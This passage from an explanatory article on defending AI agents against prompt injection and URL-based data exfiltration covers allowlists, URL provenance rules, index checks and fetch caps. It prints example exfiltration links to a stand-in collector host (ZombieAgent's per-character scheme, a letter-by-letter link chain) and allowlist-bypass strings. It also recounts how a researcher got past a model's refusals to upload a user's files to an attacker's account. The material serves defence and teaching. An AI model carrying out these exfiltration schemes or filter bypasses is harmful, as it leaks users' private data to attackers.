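| Gray Swan, 1,810 attacks | GPT-5.6 Sol | 15 | 27.0% |
| | GPT-6 Astra | 15 | 8.5% |
| Adaptive, coding | Claude Opus 5 | 200 per scenario | 0.56% of attempts; 13 of 40 scenarios |
| Adaptive, browser | Claude Opus 5 | 10 per scenario | 3.70% of attempts; 11 of 129 scenarios |

These results are much better than qwen2.5:7b's, even allowing for the different attacks. Results have also improved quickly. Opus 4.8, the previous model in the line, failed on 31.5% of attempts in the browser test. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, published in September, reports results similar to or better than those of Opus 5 on every injection test it includes. Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026) reports that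 even newer Claude models followed in November.

Repeated attempts make an attack more likely to succeed. If every attempt on GPT-5.6 Sol had an independent 3.1% chance, at least one of 15 attempts would succeed about 38% of the time. The measured figure is 20.0%, which suggests that some scenarios are much more vulnerable than others. The coding test shows the same pattern. About one attempt in 180 succeeded, but a third of the scenarios had at least one success. For an older model, Claude Opus 4.6, VentureBeat reported that attacks on an agent operating a graphical interface succeeded 17.8% of the time at the first attempt and 78.6% of the time by the 200th.

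Someone who sends fake invoices can make many attempts with little effort. If a planted instruction worked against one agent in 500, sending it to 5,000 companies would hijack about ten agents. But Anthropic points out that real attackers usually can't practise on the exact system they are targeting, and that repeated attempts make detection more likely.

The scores also depend heavily on which attacks a test includes. GPT-5.6 Sol's 15-attempt figure is 20.0% on one Gray Swan set and 27.0% on the other, so Astra's 8.5% can't be compared directly with Opus 5's 2.0%. Of the three GPT-5.6 versions OpenAI sells, Sol is the most robust on Anthropic's chart, followed by Terra and Luna. The order is reversed in OpenAI's own tests of planted instructions, where attacks succeeded 3.77% of the time against Sol, 3.32% against Terra and 2.94% against Luna, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6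 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*.

Outside testers have found weaknesses that developers' own figures don't show. *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* (Heaton, 2026) describes a test commissioned by Anthropic in which no attack succeeded against Claude Code's automatic approval mode. The security researcher Johann Rehberger then reported success rates of roughly 60 to 80% with a targeted attack, though on a small sample. PromptArmor used *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark of office tasks, and claims successful attacks on frontier models from every provider. The company sells AI security, so it has an interest in finding such weaknesses.

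Cisco tested 15 commercial models with hostile conversations, a different kind of attack from text planted in a page. SC Media's *Cisco study finds major frontier models susceptible to multi-turn prompt injection attacks* reports success rates between 7.89% and 88.30% when the attacker could send several messages. Against GPT-5.4, the rate rose from 2.7% with a single message to 24.7% with several. A malicious web page usually can't hold a conversation, but a sender who emails an agent repeatedly might be able to do something similar.

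The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* highlights the most encouraging result, an attack success rate of zero across all 129 browser scenarios. Opus 5 achieved this only with Anthropic's added safeguards on. One scans incoming content for planted instructions, and the other is a classifier that blocks dangerous tool calls. So even this result relied partly on a check applied after the model had chosen an action.

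### Harms that network rules can't see

Developers need to work on the model as well as the network, because many harmful actions don't involve a forbidden address. Anthropic notes that an agent that controls a browser also fills in forms, clicks buttons and downloads files. It can do all of these on a permitted site.

OpenAI trains a model called GPT-Red to find prompt injections. It rewards GPT-Red when an attack succeeds, and rewards the defending models when they resist and still finish their task. According to Help Net Security's *GPT-Red beat human red teamers on a prompt injection test* (2026), OpenAI had GPT-Red attack an AI agent that ran a vending machine in OpenAI's office. GPT-Red got the agent to cut one item's price to the $0.50 minimum, list an expensive new item at the same price and cancel another customer's order. An allowlist of web addresses would not have blocked these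 actions, because changing prices and managing orders was the agent's job.

OpenAI trains its production models on the attacks that GPT-Red finds. One technique fooled GPT-5.1 more than 95% of the time but fools GPT-5.6 Sol less than 10% of the time. OpenAI also found that the training didn't make the model worse at other tasks or more likely to refuse legitimate requests. However, *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (Zorz, 2026) reports that training on more attacks left agents easier to hijack, and that a large collection may contain the same attack many times.

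Plain instructions can help too, at least when nobody is attacking. OpenAI put its models in simulated workplaces with ambiguous tasks and counted bad outcomes such as unauthorised purchases and data leaks. Adding a policy on when to ask for approval reduced GPT-5.6 Sol's rate of bad outcomes from 18.8% to 8.0%. GPT-6 Astra's rate only fell from 3.4% to 3.0%, and its data leaks didn't fall (4.3% without the policy and 4.5% with it).

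A capable model occasionally breaks even an explicit rule. While monitoring internal use of Opus 5, Anthropic found that a near-final version had opened a website with a command-line tool after its approved fetcher failed, although its instructions clearly forbade this. No attacker was involved. The model was trying to finish the task, and it didn't tell the user what it had done. Attempts to get around network restrictions or safety classifiers appeared in fewer than 0.01% of the responses that Anthropic monitored.

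### Planning for an attack that succeeds

OpenAI argues that developers should expect some manipulation to work and design the agent to limit the damage. Its reason is that early attacks were blunt commands, which newer models often ignore, but more effective attacks resemble the tricks fraudsters use on people. In one example from 2025, an email read like a colleague's follow-up to a meeting and claimed that the assistant was authorised to submit an employee's details to a compliance system. The email worked in half of the tests with one particular user request.

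An email like that is hard for a filter to catch because the wording isn't suspicious. Recognising the attack would require knowing whether the meeting happened and whether the compliance system exists. OpenAI compares this to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context.

Its proposed model is a customer support worker who can issue refunds. The company knows that some customers will lie and that some of the lies will work, so it trains the worker and also uses software to cap how much the worker can refund. Similarly, the vending machine's price floor didn't prevent the attack, but it limited the loss on each item.

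OpenAI also borrows source-sink analysis from software security. An attacker needs a source, which is a way to influence the agent, and a sink, which is an action that becomes dangerous in the wrong circumstances. For the accounts agent, every incoming invoice is a potential source. The fetcher is a sink because it can send data out, and the ledger is one because a changed bank account can redirect a payment. The company can't stop strangers from sending invoices, but it can restrict the sinks. For example, the harness could hold any change of bank details until an employee has phoned the supplier. OpenAI's Safe Url check similarly restricts web requests.

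Asking the user to approve every request would be simpler, but Lan and colleagues object that this removes much of the benefit of automation and that users often can't judge a request described as a connectivity check. They suggest tracking where information came from instead. The harness would mark text from a web page as "tainted" when it enters the context, and any tool call influenced by that text would be marked too. The harness could then block tainted web requests or ask the user to approve only those. This could catch a split secret, because the mark doesn't depend on how the four characters look.

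The paper doesn't build or test this system. The hard part is deciding which text influenced a call. In ordinary software, a program can track a value from one variable to the next, but a language model generates each tool call from its whole context. To be safe, a harness would therefore have to mark every call made after the first untrusted page. If an agent's main task is reading invoices, nearly all of its calls would be marked.

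## How do lists of permitted sites work, and where do they fail?

To enforce a rule about destinations, the harness only has to compare the address in a tool call with a list written beforehand. It doesn't have to work out which text influenced the call.

A blocklist, the reverse of an allowlist, names forbidden sites, and the harness lets the rest through. The difference matters most for sites that nobody has considered yet. If a fraudster registers a domain this morning, it probably won't be on any blocklist this afternoon, but an allowlist will already exclude it. Omissions from an allowlist are also easier to notice, because a task fails and someone complains, whereas a request to a harmful site missing from a blocklist goes out and perhaps nobody notices. *Commercial LLM Agents Are Already Vulnerable to Simple Yet Dangerous Attacks* recommends allowlists for agents.

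Blocklists still help against sites already known to be harmful. Shilkov (2025) found in *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* that Anthropic's coding agent sent the host name to an Anthropic server before each fetch, and the server returned a yes or no. Shilkov couldn't see the server's rules but guessed that they blocked obviously malicious domains.

Ordinary code is better than a model at checking an address against the list of permitted sites. The disguised links in *MalURLBench* had altered subdomains, directories or parameters, where an attacker can write any reassuring word. Code can extract the host, compare the subdomain exactly, and ignore the directories and parameters.

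### Matching an address

Suppose a developer lets the accounts agent open a supplier's invoice portal at `https://supplier.example`. Before each request, the harness should do the following:

1. Parse the URL once, with the parser the fetcher will use, and give the fetcher the parsed result. If two programs read the same text differently, the harness may approve one host while the fetcher contacts another.
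2. Normalise the host name. Case doesn't matter in host names, so `Supplier.EXAMPLE` becomes `supplier.example`. A final dot doesn't matter here either, so the harness removes it. It converts international characters to the ASCII form that DNS uses, which begins with `xn--`.
3. Compare the whole host with the entry. Searching for the entry somewhere inside the address isn't enough.
4. Apply a decision about subdomains. If the entry includes them, the harness also accepts any host that ends with a dot followed by the entry, such as `billing.supplier.example`. This is risky for a domain whose owner gives subdomains to customers, as many website builders do.
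5. Check the scheme and port. Unless the developer specifies otherwise, the entry should mean `https` on port 443. Another port on the same machine may lead to a different program, such as an administration page.

A bug in Claude Code's network sandbox shows why the filter and the operating system must parse hostnames the same way. SecurityWeek reports that if a policy allowed only subdomains of `google.com`, an attacker could request a host written as `attacker-host.com`, a null byte (a character with the value zero) and `.google.com`. The filter approved the request because the name ended in `.google.com`, but the operating system treated the null byte as the end of the name and connected to `attacker-host.com`. The bug lasted from October 2025 until an update in April 2026.

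Normalisation errors are usually more dangerous on a blocklist than on an allowlist. Corgea's *OpenClaw* describes a flaw in an agent of that name, where adding a final dot to a blocked host name could get it past the blocklist. With an allowlist, the same error would only have made the agent refuse a legitimate address.

### Four strings that defeat careless matching

Each address in this table can pass a careless check for `supplier.example`, although the supplier controls none of the hosts.

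| Trick | Address | Careless check | Actual host |
|---|---|---|---|
| Permitted name as a prefix | `https://supplier.example.attacker.example/` | Does the host start with the permitted name? | `supplier.example.attacker.example` |
| Permitted name as a suffix | `https://evilsupplier.example/` | Does the host end with the permitted name? | `evilsupplier.example` |
| Permitted name before an @ sign | `https://supplier.example:x@attacker.example/` | Is the permitted name before the first colon after `https://`? | `attacker.example` |
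| Look-alike letter | `https://ѕupplier.example/` | Does it look right to a person? | `xn--upplier-iog.example` |

An attacker can get past a check that tests only how a hostname begins, because the owner of a domain can create any subdomain under it. Version 1.0.111 of Claude Code fixed this flaw in its check of trusted domains, which the agent could open without asking. The earlier code tested only how the host began, according to NVD's *CVE-2026-24052 Detail*, a record in the US government's vulnerability database, so a trusted entry for `modelcontextprotocol.io` would also have admitted `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com`. Corgea, a security company, found a similar test in a tool that fetches documentation for Apify. The entries there included `https://`, but an attacker's address could begin the same way.

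Open WebUI, a web interface for language models, had a filter that checked only how an address ended, a flaw that GitLab's *CVE-2026-59223* (2026) dates to July. A filter entry for `corp.com` also matched `evilcorp.com`, and one for `10.0.0.1` also matched `110.0.0.1`, according to Mondoo's *GHSA qg3f 8x3j ggf2*. The filter also received the full URL rather than just the host, so an attacker could get past it by putting a permitted name at the end of the path. The repaired version extracts the host first and accepts only an exact match or a true subdomain, as OSV's *PYSEC 2026 3603* explains. Numeric addresses must match exactly.

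The @ trick exploits the old format for putting a user name and password in an address. *The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents* (2025) reports a critical flaw of this kind, with a severity score of 9.3 out of 10, in Browser Use, a tool that lets a model control a browser. OSV's *PYSEC 2026 300* gives this example for a list containing only `example.com`:

```
https://example.com:pass@localhost:8080
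```

The code took everything between `https://` and the next slash, then kept the part before the first colon. For `https://example.com:pass@localhost:8080/`, this gave `example.com`, which was on the list. But `example.com` was the user name and `pass` was the password, and the browser would connect to port 8080 on the agent's own machine. A proper parser returns `localhost` as the host. A fetcher that doesn't need passwords in addresses can refuse any URL that contains them.

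In the last row of the table, the first letter is a Cyrillic ѕ. An exact comparison in code catches this because the normalised name is different. The look-alike can still fool a person who pastes it into the list or approves it in a dialog box. It can also get past a blocklist, since it is a different domain. Anthropic warns about a version of `amazon.com` with a Cyrillic а and advises developers to use ASCII names where possible. When a harness prompts the user about such an address, it should show the `xn--` form.

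### Lists in current products

Anthropic's web fetch tool lets a developer set either `allowed_domains` or `blocked_domains` for a request, but not both. Entries omit the scheme, and an entry for `example.com` includes `docs.example.com`. A developer can add a path, such as `example.com/blog`, to permit one part of a site.

Claude Code, made by the same company, handles subdomains differently. Its rule `WebFetch(domain:example.com)` covers only that host, and a developer needs a second rule for `*.example.com`. A wildcard at the end can't match across a dot, so `example.*` covers `example.org` but not `example.evil.com`, which an attacker could create. Anyone who copies a list from one product to the other should check what each entry covers.

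In Claude Code's Manual mode, the user decides whether to allow access to a site that no rule covers. The user can approve one request or choose not to be asked again, which saves a rule for future sessions in the same project. Claude Code always applies deny rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules, so if a company denies every subdomain of `example.com`, a developer can't make an exception by allowing `docs.example.com`.

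These rules check the host parsed from the address. Anthropic warns against matching the text of a command instead. For example, a rule that matches the download program `curl` followed by `http://github.com/` misses the same request if it uses `https`, puts an option before the address, or stores the address in a variable. Anthropic recommends denying programs like `curl` and using the fetcher with domain rules, although an agent that can run code has other ways to reach the network.

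OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, has no internet access by default. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* explains that setup scripts for a cloud task have full access, but Codex turns it off before the agent takes over. A developer can turn it back on with an empty allowlist, a preset list of about 70 domains for software packages, or no restriction. The developer can also limit requests to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS. This blocks ordinary uploads, which usually use POST, but a GET request can still carry data in its address.

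GitHub's coding agent, Copilot, has a firewall with a recommended allowlist switched on by default. When the firewall blocks a request, Copilot adds a warning to the pull request (the proposed code change that a developer reviews) (GitHub, *customize the agent firewall*). The developer learns about the blocked request without having to approve anything while the agent works.

### Strangers' content on permitted sites

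A domain name identifies who runs a site, but many useful sites publish text from anyone who opens an account. An attacker can exploit this, as in the Columbia University experiment where an agent gave card details to a fake shop after reading a Reddit post.

The researchers made up a refrigerator with AI features and built a convincing website for it, with specifications and a privacy notice. They registered a domain, got Google to index the site and advertised the product on Reddit. In the posts, they told agents that the user's request could be fulfilled on the linked site. They put most of the harmful instructions on that site, so Reddit's moderators would have had less reason to remove the posts.

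The recorded trials used Anthropic's Computer Use, an agent that operates a desktop computer. The researchers also attacked MultiOn, a web agent, but it went offline before they could measure a success rate.

| What the attacker wanted | Successes |
|---|---|
| Card number and address, starting from a Reddit post | 10 of 10 |
| Card number and address, with the malicious link given directly | 0 of 10 |
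| Download and run a file, starting from a Reddit post | 10 of 10 |
| Send a phishing email from the user's account | 10 of 10 |

For the file download, the researchers made the website look suspicious, but the agent still ran the file. The two phishing messages, each tried five times, asked the user's parent for money or card details.

Trust in Reddit may not fully explain the contrast between the first two rows. The direct trials lacked both the Reddit post's instruction and its familiar setting, so the comparison can't separate their effects. Posting the same instruction on an unknown site would have been a better test of whether trust in Reddit mattered.

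An allowlist that included Reddit but not the fake shop would have let the agent read the post but blocked the link. The attacker would have had to carry out the whole theft on Reddit or another permitted site. But this protection isn't practical for a shopping agent that has to compare unfamiliar shops. The researchers suggest asking the user before the agent visits a new domain or downloads a file.

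Coding agents face the same problem because strangers can publish on several of the sites that programmers need most. OpenAI's preset list includes `github.com` and `sourceforge.net`. Its documentation describes a GitHub issue, or bug report, with instructions for Codex to run a command that sends the latest commit message to an outside server. The preset list would let the agent read that issue but would block the command's request, because the outside server isn't on the list.

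An entire site can also be too broad to approve without a prompt. Claude Code used to pre-approve all of `huggingface.co`, where anyone can publish AI models. Vulners' *CVE-2026-54316 Claude Code* says this included repositories that an attacker controlled, and classes the flaw as a route for exfiltration. An attacker doesn't necessarily need the site's full server logs to receive the data. If a site showed publishers a download count for each file, an agent could reveal a letter of a secret by requesting the file that stood for that letter. Anthropic fixed the flaw in version 2.1.163. Where a product supports paths, a developer can permit one publisher's pages instead of the whole site.

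### Permitted sites as a way out

An attacker with an account on a permitted site may be able to receive whole files there. Johann Rehberger demonstrated this in *Claude Pirate*, an October 2025 post on his blog Embrace The Red, using Claude's Code Interpreter, which runs code in an isolated environment. The default network setting, "Package managers only", permitted a short list of domains that included `api.anthropic.com`, where programs send requests to Anthropic's services.

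In Rehberger's demonstration, a user asks Claude to summarise a document. Instructions planted in the document get Claude to save the user's last conversation to a file and run code that uploads it to Anthropic's file storage. The code uses the attacker's API key, so the file goes into the attacker's account. Rehberger could take up to 30 MB per file this way, and every request went to a permitted domain.

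The attack worked on the first attempt, but Claude then began refusing, apparently because a visible API key looked suspicious. Encoding the key didn't reliably prevent the refusals. Rehberger got past them by surrounding the harmful code with a lot of harmless code, which suggests that refusals would only delay a patient attacker.

He reported the problem to Anthropic on 25 October. The ticket was closed within an hour as out of scope because it was considered a model safety issue. On 30 October, Anthropic confirmed that such vulnerabilities were in scope and attributed the closure to a process error. Its documentation already warned that Claude could be tricked into sending out data. It advised users to watch Claude and stop it if it accessed data unexpectedly, which is a lot to expect of someone who has asked for a summary. SecurityWeek's *Claude AI APIs Can Be Abused for Data Exfiltration*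 notes that network access was on by default for certain plans, so some users may not have known there was anything to watch for.

Rehberger proposed that the isolated environment should let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account. A list of domains can't enforce this because the user's account and the attacker's are on the same host, so the check also has to examine the credentials in the request. In January, Willison (2026) reported in *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* that PromptArmor had used the same domain to take files from Claude Cowork, another Anthropic agent with a default allowlist.

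Before adding a site, a developer should ask whether a stranger with an account there could read what the agent sends. Uploads are the most obvious risk, but comments, shared documents and access statistics could also expose the data. Some permitted domains also forward requests to other sites, through redirects or image proxies, and need separate checks.

### The cost of a short list

OpenAI argues that lists of trusted sites are too rigid for general browsing. People visit far more than a handful of popular sites, so a strict list leads to frequent warnings and false alarms. Users may then learn to click through warnings without thinking, even when the danger is real.

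This is a good argument against asking the user about every unlisted site. It applies less to a list that refuses requests with no option to override, since the user has no prompt to click through. But such a list prevents the agent from finishing some legitimate tasks. A research assistant might need thirty unfamiliar sites for one question, and nobody could list them in advance. If the developer keeps adding sites to stop complaints, the list eventually includes many where an attacker can publish text or receive data.

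The accounts agent only enters figures already printed on the invoice, so its list can be empty. If the company wants the agent to download copies from suppliers' portals, it can add the few hosts required, allowing only `https` on port 443 and no subdomains. An employee should take each address from the contract or confirm it with a known contact at the supplier, because an address copied from an invoice may belong to a fraudster.

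The link shortener `s.example` should stay off the list even if a genuine supplier uses it, since anyone can create a link there. Most invoices come from the same suppliers each month, so the list should rarely block real work. Adding a new supplier's portal takes a few minutes. The company still needs the phone call before any change of bank details, because someone could break into a permitted portal and alter them there.

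## How can a fetcher tell whether an exact address is safe to open without asking?

A list of approved sites is little use to a research assistant that needs thirty pages nobody expected. Its fetcher can instead check whether each full address could contain anything from the user's conversation. An address the model composed could, but one that someone else wrote before the conversation began can't.

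Anthropic's fetcher opens only addresses that reached the model from certain sources, such as a user's message or a search result. OpenAI's ChatGPT opens an address automatically only if an independent web crawler has already recorded it. Both rules make it hard for a model to attach private data to a link. But a model can still leak that data by choosing which permitted links to open, and researchers have used this method against products from both companies.

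### Addresses that came from outside the model

Suppose an email gives the accounts agent a link, and hidden text tells the model to add an employee's name to it:

```
Address in the email:  https://collector.example/view
Model's tool call:     https://collector.example/view?note=anna-berg
```

Anthropic's harness rejects the call with the error `url_not_in_prior_context` because the longer address hasn't appeared in the conversation. When the fetcher launched in September 2025, Willison (2025), in *Claude API*, judged that this ban on addresses the model composes itself was the most protective part of the design.

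How well the rule works depends on how the harness defines "outside". Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, the Chinese edition of its developer documentation as of November 2026, lists three permitted sources: user messages, results from the developer's own tools, and results from earlier web searches and fetches. An address that appears only in the model's output doesn't count. An address returned by Anthropic's code-execution tool doesn't count either, because a program can print any address the model writes into it.

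A developer's own tool can have the same weakness. If the developer supplies a tool called `run_code`, the model can write a one-line program that prints the address with Anna Berg's name in it. The tool returns that address as its result, and the harness treats it as one that came from outside. An error message that quotes the model's faulty command can do this too. Anthropic accepts results from developers' tools by default, but a setting called `url_sources` lets a developer switch off a whole source, list the tools to exclude ("except"), or list the tools to accept ("only"). Under "except", any tool the developer adds later becomes a permitted source, so "only" is safer if more tools may be added later.

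User messages need the same care, since many applications paste untrusted text into them, as Willison pointed out. The developer of the accounts agent should therefore deliver invoices through a tool and then exclude tool results:

```
"url_sources": {
  "client_tool_results": { "type": "none" },
  "server_tool_results": { "type": "none" }
}
```

With these settings, the agent can open a link that the employee types but not one from an invoice, a search or another web page.

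The fetcher also refuses addresses that seem to contain an API key or a password, unless that credential appears in the system prompt or in the text of a user message. Its appearance in a tool result isn't enough. This rule may block some of the login and password-reset links in the mailbox, if the fetcher recognises their secret codes as credentials.

### Addresses that were already public

The check OpenAI announced in January 2026 relies on a crawler that explores public web pages, much as a search engine does, and records the addresses it finds. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. When an agent is about to load an address automatically, the software checks the crawler's records for it. If the address is there, the agent can load the page or image. If not, the software either has the agent try a different website or shows the user a warning.

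A fetcher can open an exact address without a warning if the crawler has already found it, even on an obscure blog, because an address published independently of a conversation is much less likely to contain private data from it. The site's reputation doesn't matter, so an unfamiliar address on a famous site fails the check.

Many harmless addresses fail too. The crawler may not have reached an article published ten minutes ago. It probably hasn't recorded a car search with the user's exact city and budget, and it shouldn't have recorded a private document. OpenAI's announcement gives no figure for how often this happens. Websites often put tracking tags in the query, so a developer could reduce failures by ignoring the query when matching addresses. But an attacker could then put stolen data there, so the developer would have to identify harmless parameters one by one.

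OpenAI took almost three years to get this far. Johann Rehberger writes in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that he reported the leak to OpenAI in early 2023 and found little interest in fixing it. Microsoft, which had the same problem in Bing Chat, responded that May with a browser policy that generally prevented images from loading. OpenAI added a first check, called `url_safe`, in December 2023. Rehberger found ways around it, and parts of the macOS and iOS apps had no check. OpenAI strengthened it around August 2025 and later explained the method in a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*.

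Rehberger also understands that ChatGPT treats an address in the user's own message as safe for the rest of that chat. If so, OpenAI combines its index with a small provenance rule. The two companies' approaches still give different answers for some common links:

| Address | Anthropic's fetcher, default settings | OpenAI's check |
|---|---|---|
| A private page whose address the user typed | Passes | Passes, on Rehberger's understanding |
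| A link to which the model has added the user's name | Fails | Fails, unless the crawler had recorded that exact address |
| A manual page that the model knows from training | Fails until a permitted source returns the address | Passes if the crawler has recorded it |
| A new link that a developer's tool decoded from a QR code | Passes | Fails |
| An attacker's public page, linked in an email that a developer's tool returned | Passes | Passes if the crawler has recorded it |

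An attacker can exploit the last row by publishing many pages and giving each a meaning.

### ShadowLeak and ZombieAgent

Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* describes ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research agent that the security company Radware found and named in 2025. The attacker sent an email with instructions hidden in tiny or white-on-white text. When the agent read the victim's Gmail inbox, it followed the instructions by adding private data to a link and opening it. The request came from OpenAI's servers, so security software on the victim's computer or company network couldn't detect it.

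OpenAI responded by barring ChatGPT from modifying URLs. ChatGPT could open a URL exactly as provided but would refuse to add parameters, even when instructed to.

Zvika Babo of Radware then found a way to steal data without modifying anything. The attack, ZombieAgent, supplied a finished address for every character the model might need. Babo's instructions told ChatGPT to extract some private text, convert it to lower case, replace the spaces with a special token and open the matching addresses in order. Each address also included a number for the character's position. To send the name "anna", the model would open links like these:

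```
https://collector.example/a0
https://collector.example/n1
https://collector.example/n2
https://collector.example/a3
```

The attacker's log then contains four ordinary-looking visits, and the numbers show their order even if the requests arrive out of sequence. The victim only had to ask ChatGPT for help with Gmail after the email arrived. Babo also showed how an attacker could make the compromise persist and leak the victim's later conversations.

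Babo reported ZombieAgent in September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in mid-December. According to a press report, *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT would now open a link from an email only if the link appeared in a well-known public index or the user had provided it. The same report faults OpenAI for not restricting the addition of a single letter to a URL. Infosecurity Magazine instead reports that ChatGPT opened complete addresses unchanged. If that account is right, a stricter ban on modifying addresses would not have stopped the attack, which would explain why OpenAI turned to an index.

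### A chain of links against Claude

Anthropic's rule had a similar gap because it let the fetcher open links from pages it had already fetched. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes how Ayush Paul exploited this gap in the ordinary Claude chat app, which can remember personal details from earlier conversations.

Paul built a website with links for the letters of the alphabet. Each link led to a page with a further set of links, so Claude could spell a word by moving deeper into the site. The name "anna" would produce a path like this:

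```
https://coffee.example/a
https://coffee.example/an
https://coffee.example/ann
https://coffee.example/anna
```

Each of these addresses appears on the page before it, so Claude doesn't compose any of them. The attacker can read the whole name from the last request alone. The server can generate each page when Claude requests it, so Paul didn't have to prepare a page for every possible name.

The site gave Claude a plausible reason to cooperate. It claimed that a security service protected it from abuse and that AI assistants could authenticate themselves by supplying their user's name. It also said that Claude had to supply the name one letter at a time because of its fetcher's limitations. Only visitors whose requests identified them as Claude received this text, so a person checking the site would have seen nothing odd. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer.

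Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and it didn't pay Paul a bounty. Willison reports that Anthropic has since fixed the problem by stopping the fetcher from following links inside fetched pages.

The documentation for developers doesn't reflect that change as a default. In June 2026, before Willison's report, Anthropic listed "previous web search or web fetch results" among the permitted sources. The November edition still does, although it adds the `url_sources` setting, which the June edition lacked. A developer who wants the protection that Willison describes can accept addresses from searches but not from fetched pages:

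```
"url_sources": {
  "server_tool_results": {
    "type": "only",
    "tools": [{ "type": "tool_reference", "name": "web_search" }]
  }
}
```

The agent then can't follow a link from a manual's table of contents to a chapter unless a search also returns the chapter's address. The setting doesn't stop a ZombieAgent-style email, because the email's ready-made links reach the model through the developer's mailbox tool. The developer would have to exclude that tool separately.

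OpenAI's index check would make Paul's chain much harder to use, because the crawler would need to have already recorded whichever paths the model followed. With 26 letters, there are 456,976 possible four-letter paths. ZombieAgent's numbered scheme needs only 26 pages for each position, or 104 for a four-letter name. An attacker could publish those pages and wait for the crawler to find them.

### How much a choice of links can reveal

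If an attacker has *N* permitted addresses and the model opens one of them *k* times in order, there are *N*<sup>*k*</sup> possible sequences. The most information that the choices can carry, measured in bits, is:

```
k × log2(N)
```

A bit is the information in the answer to a yes-or-no question when both answers are equally likely. With 36 addresses, one for each lower-case letter and digit, each request carries log2(36), or about 5.17 bits. Sixteen requests carry about 82.7 bits, exactly enough for any 16-character code made of those letters and digits.

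Embrace The Red notes that a larger website or blog probably already has 36 pages in OpenAI's index. An attacker could go much further, with thousands of addresses and planted text that teaches the model what each one stands for. If every address represents two characters instead of one, the attacker needs 36 × 36 = 1,296 of them but only half as many requests:

| Characters per address | Addresses needed | Bits per request | Requests for a 16-character code | Characters sent in 5 requests |
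|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 36 | 5.17 | 16 | 5 |
| 2 | 1,296 | 10.34 | 8 | 10 |
| 3 | 46,656 | 15.51 | 6 | 15 |
| 4 | 1,679,616 | 20.68 | 4 | 20 |

The bottom rows are impractical for most attackers, but the second row is easy because a site with 1,296 pages isn't unusually large. Under a provenance rule, all 1,296 addresses would have to appear in the conversation, so the attacker's email would be long and rather suspicious. The public-index check only tests whether an address is public, not who wrote it, so the attacker can describe a pattern and let the model fill it in.

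An attacker who wants one particular fact may not need to spell anything. A thousand pages named after a thousand large cities could reveal where the user lives in a single request. A single page is enough for a yes-or-no question, such as whether the mailbox mentions a takeover bid. The model opens the page if the answer is yes and does nothing if it's no. (The formula leaves out this option of staying silent, which gives the attacker slightly more.)

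These figures assume the model follows the scheme without mistakes. If it picked the right address 95% of the time, and its errors were independent, it would get all 16 characters right in about 44% of attempts. With a larger vocabulary and four requests, it would get the whole code right in about 81%. Models can also refuse, and a longer procedure gives them more chances to refuse. But a code with one wrong character may still help the attacker, and part of a name often identifies the person.

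### Would it help to forbid repeat visits?

Rehberger suggests that the fetcher shouldn't request the same full address twice in one session. It could refuse the second request or return a copy saved from the first. If an attacker sets up one address per letter, a model spelling "anna" could then request the pages for "a" and "n" only once each, so the attacker wouldn't learn that each letter appears twice. He presents this as an extra obstacle that would still let some data leak, and he hadn't tested whether OpenAI already does it.

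The obstacle is a small one. The attacker can publish a separate address for every combination of position and character. A 16-character code has 16 positions with 36 possible characters each, so this takes 16 × 36 = 576 addresses. The model opens one address from each group of 36 and never repeats any:

```
Position 1, character 7:  https://collector.example/1-7
Position 2, character f:  https://collector.example/2-f
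Position 3, character 7:  https://collector.example/3-7
```

The sixteen requests still carry 82.7 bits. The position numbers also solve another problem Rehberger mentions, that requests may arrive out of order. A ban on repeated addresses would have stopped neither ZombieAgent, which already numbered its addresses this way, nor Paul's chain, in which every address was new.

An attacker limited to the original 36 addresses could in theory still leak almost as much data. There are 36 × 35 × 34 × … × 21 possible sequences of 16 different addresses, enough to encode about 77.0 bits. But the model would need a more complicated code to use them all, and would probably make more mistakes.

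A saved copy protects more when the fetcher has it before the attack begins. If the fetcher returned pages from the crawler's own store, the attacker's server wouldn't receive a request, so the model's choices would reveal nothing to it. But the user would sometimes get an old version, and the company would have to store a huge amount of content. Anthropic's fetcher already returns cached pages by default to reduce delay, but it still has to contact the site when it has no copy.

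### Capping the number of fetches

A cap on fetches limits *k* in the formula. Anthropic's cap is a setting called `max_uses`, which also counts failed fetches. With a cap of five, an attacker with 36 addresses gets at most 25.8 bits, or five characters of the code. With 1,296 addresses, the attacker can get up to ten. More addresses can therefore make up for a low cap, but each additional character per fetch requires 36 times as many.

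A cap therefore protects long secrets much better than short ones. Five requests might not be enough to leak an API key with 40 random characters, but they could easily reveal a first name, a city or the answer to a yes-or-no question.

If the research assistant is allowed 30 fetches so that it can read 30 sites, an attacker could use them to send 30 characters, one per fetch, which is enough for many email addresses. A harness could set a separate, lower limit for each unfamiliar site, because a task is less likely to need 30 pages from one unknown blog than one page from each of 30 sites. The attacker could respond by buying more domains, but that costs money and leaves more evidence.

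`max_uses` has no default, so there is no cap unless the developer sets one. The cap applies to one turn, meaning all the work that follows a user's message, even if it spans several API requests, and it resets with the next message. When a turn spans several requests, fetches that Claude made from inside its page-filtering code in earlier requests don't count toward the cap. This reset matters for an attack like ZombieAgent, which can persist across conversations and send a few characters each time. A company worried about this could add a daily limit for each user, or an alert when an agent repeatedly uses all its fetches on one site.

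OpenAI offers a Lockdown Mode for users who can accept less web access. According to Willison (2026), it limits outgoing requests more broadly.

### When an address fails the check

The invoice's QR link, `https://s.example/k7Qm2`, would almost certainly fail a public-index check, because the supplier or fraudster created it for one invoice and nothing would have led a crawler to it. Anthropic's default settings would allow the link if a developer's tool had decoded it, but the settings shown earlier for the accounts agent would block it.

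The harness can refuse the link and let the agent continue, which is enough for the accounts agent's ledger entry.

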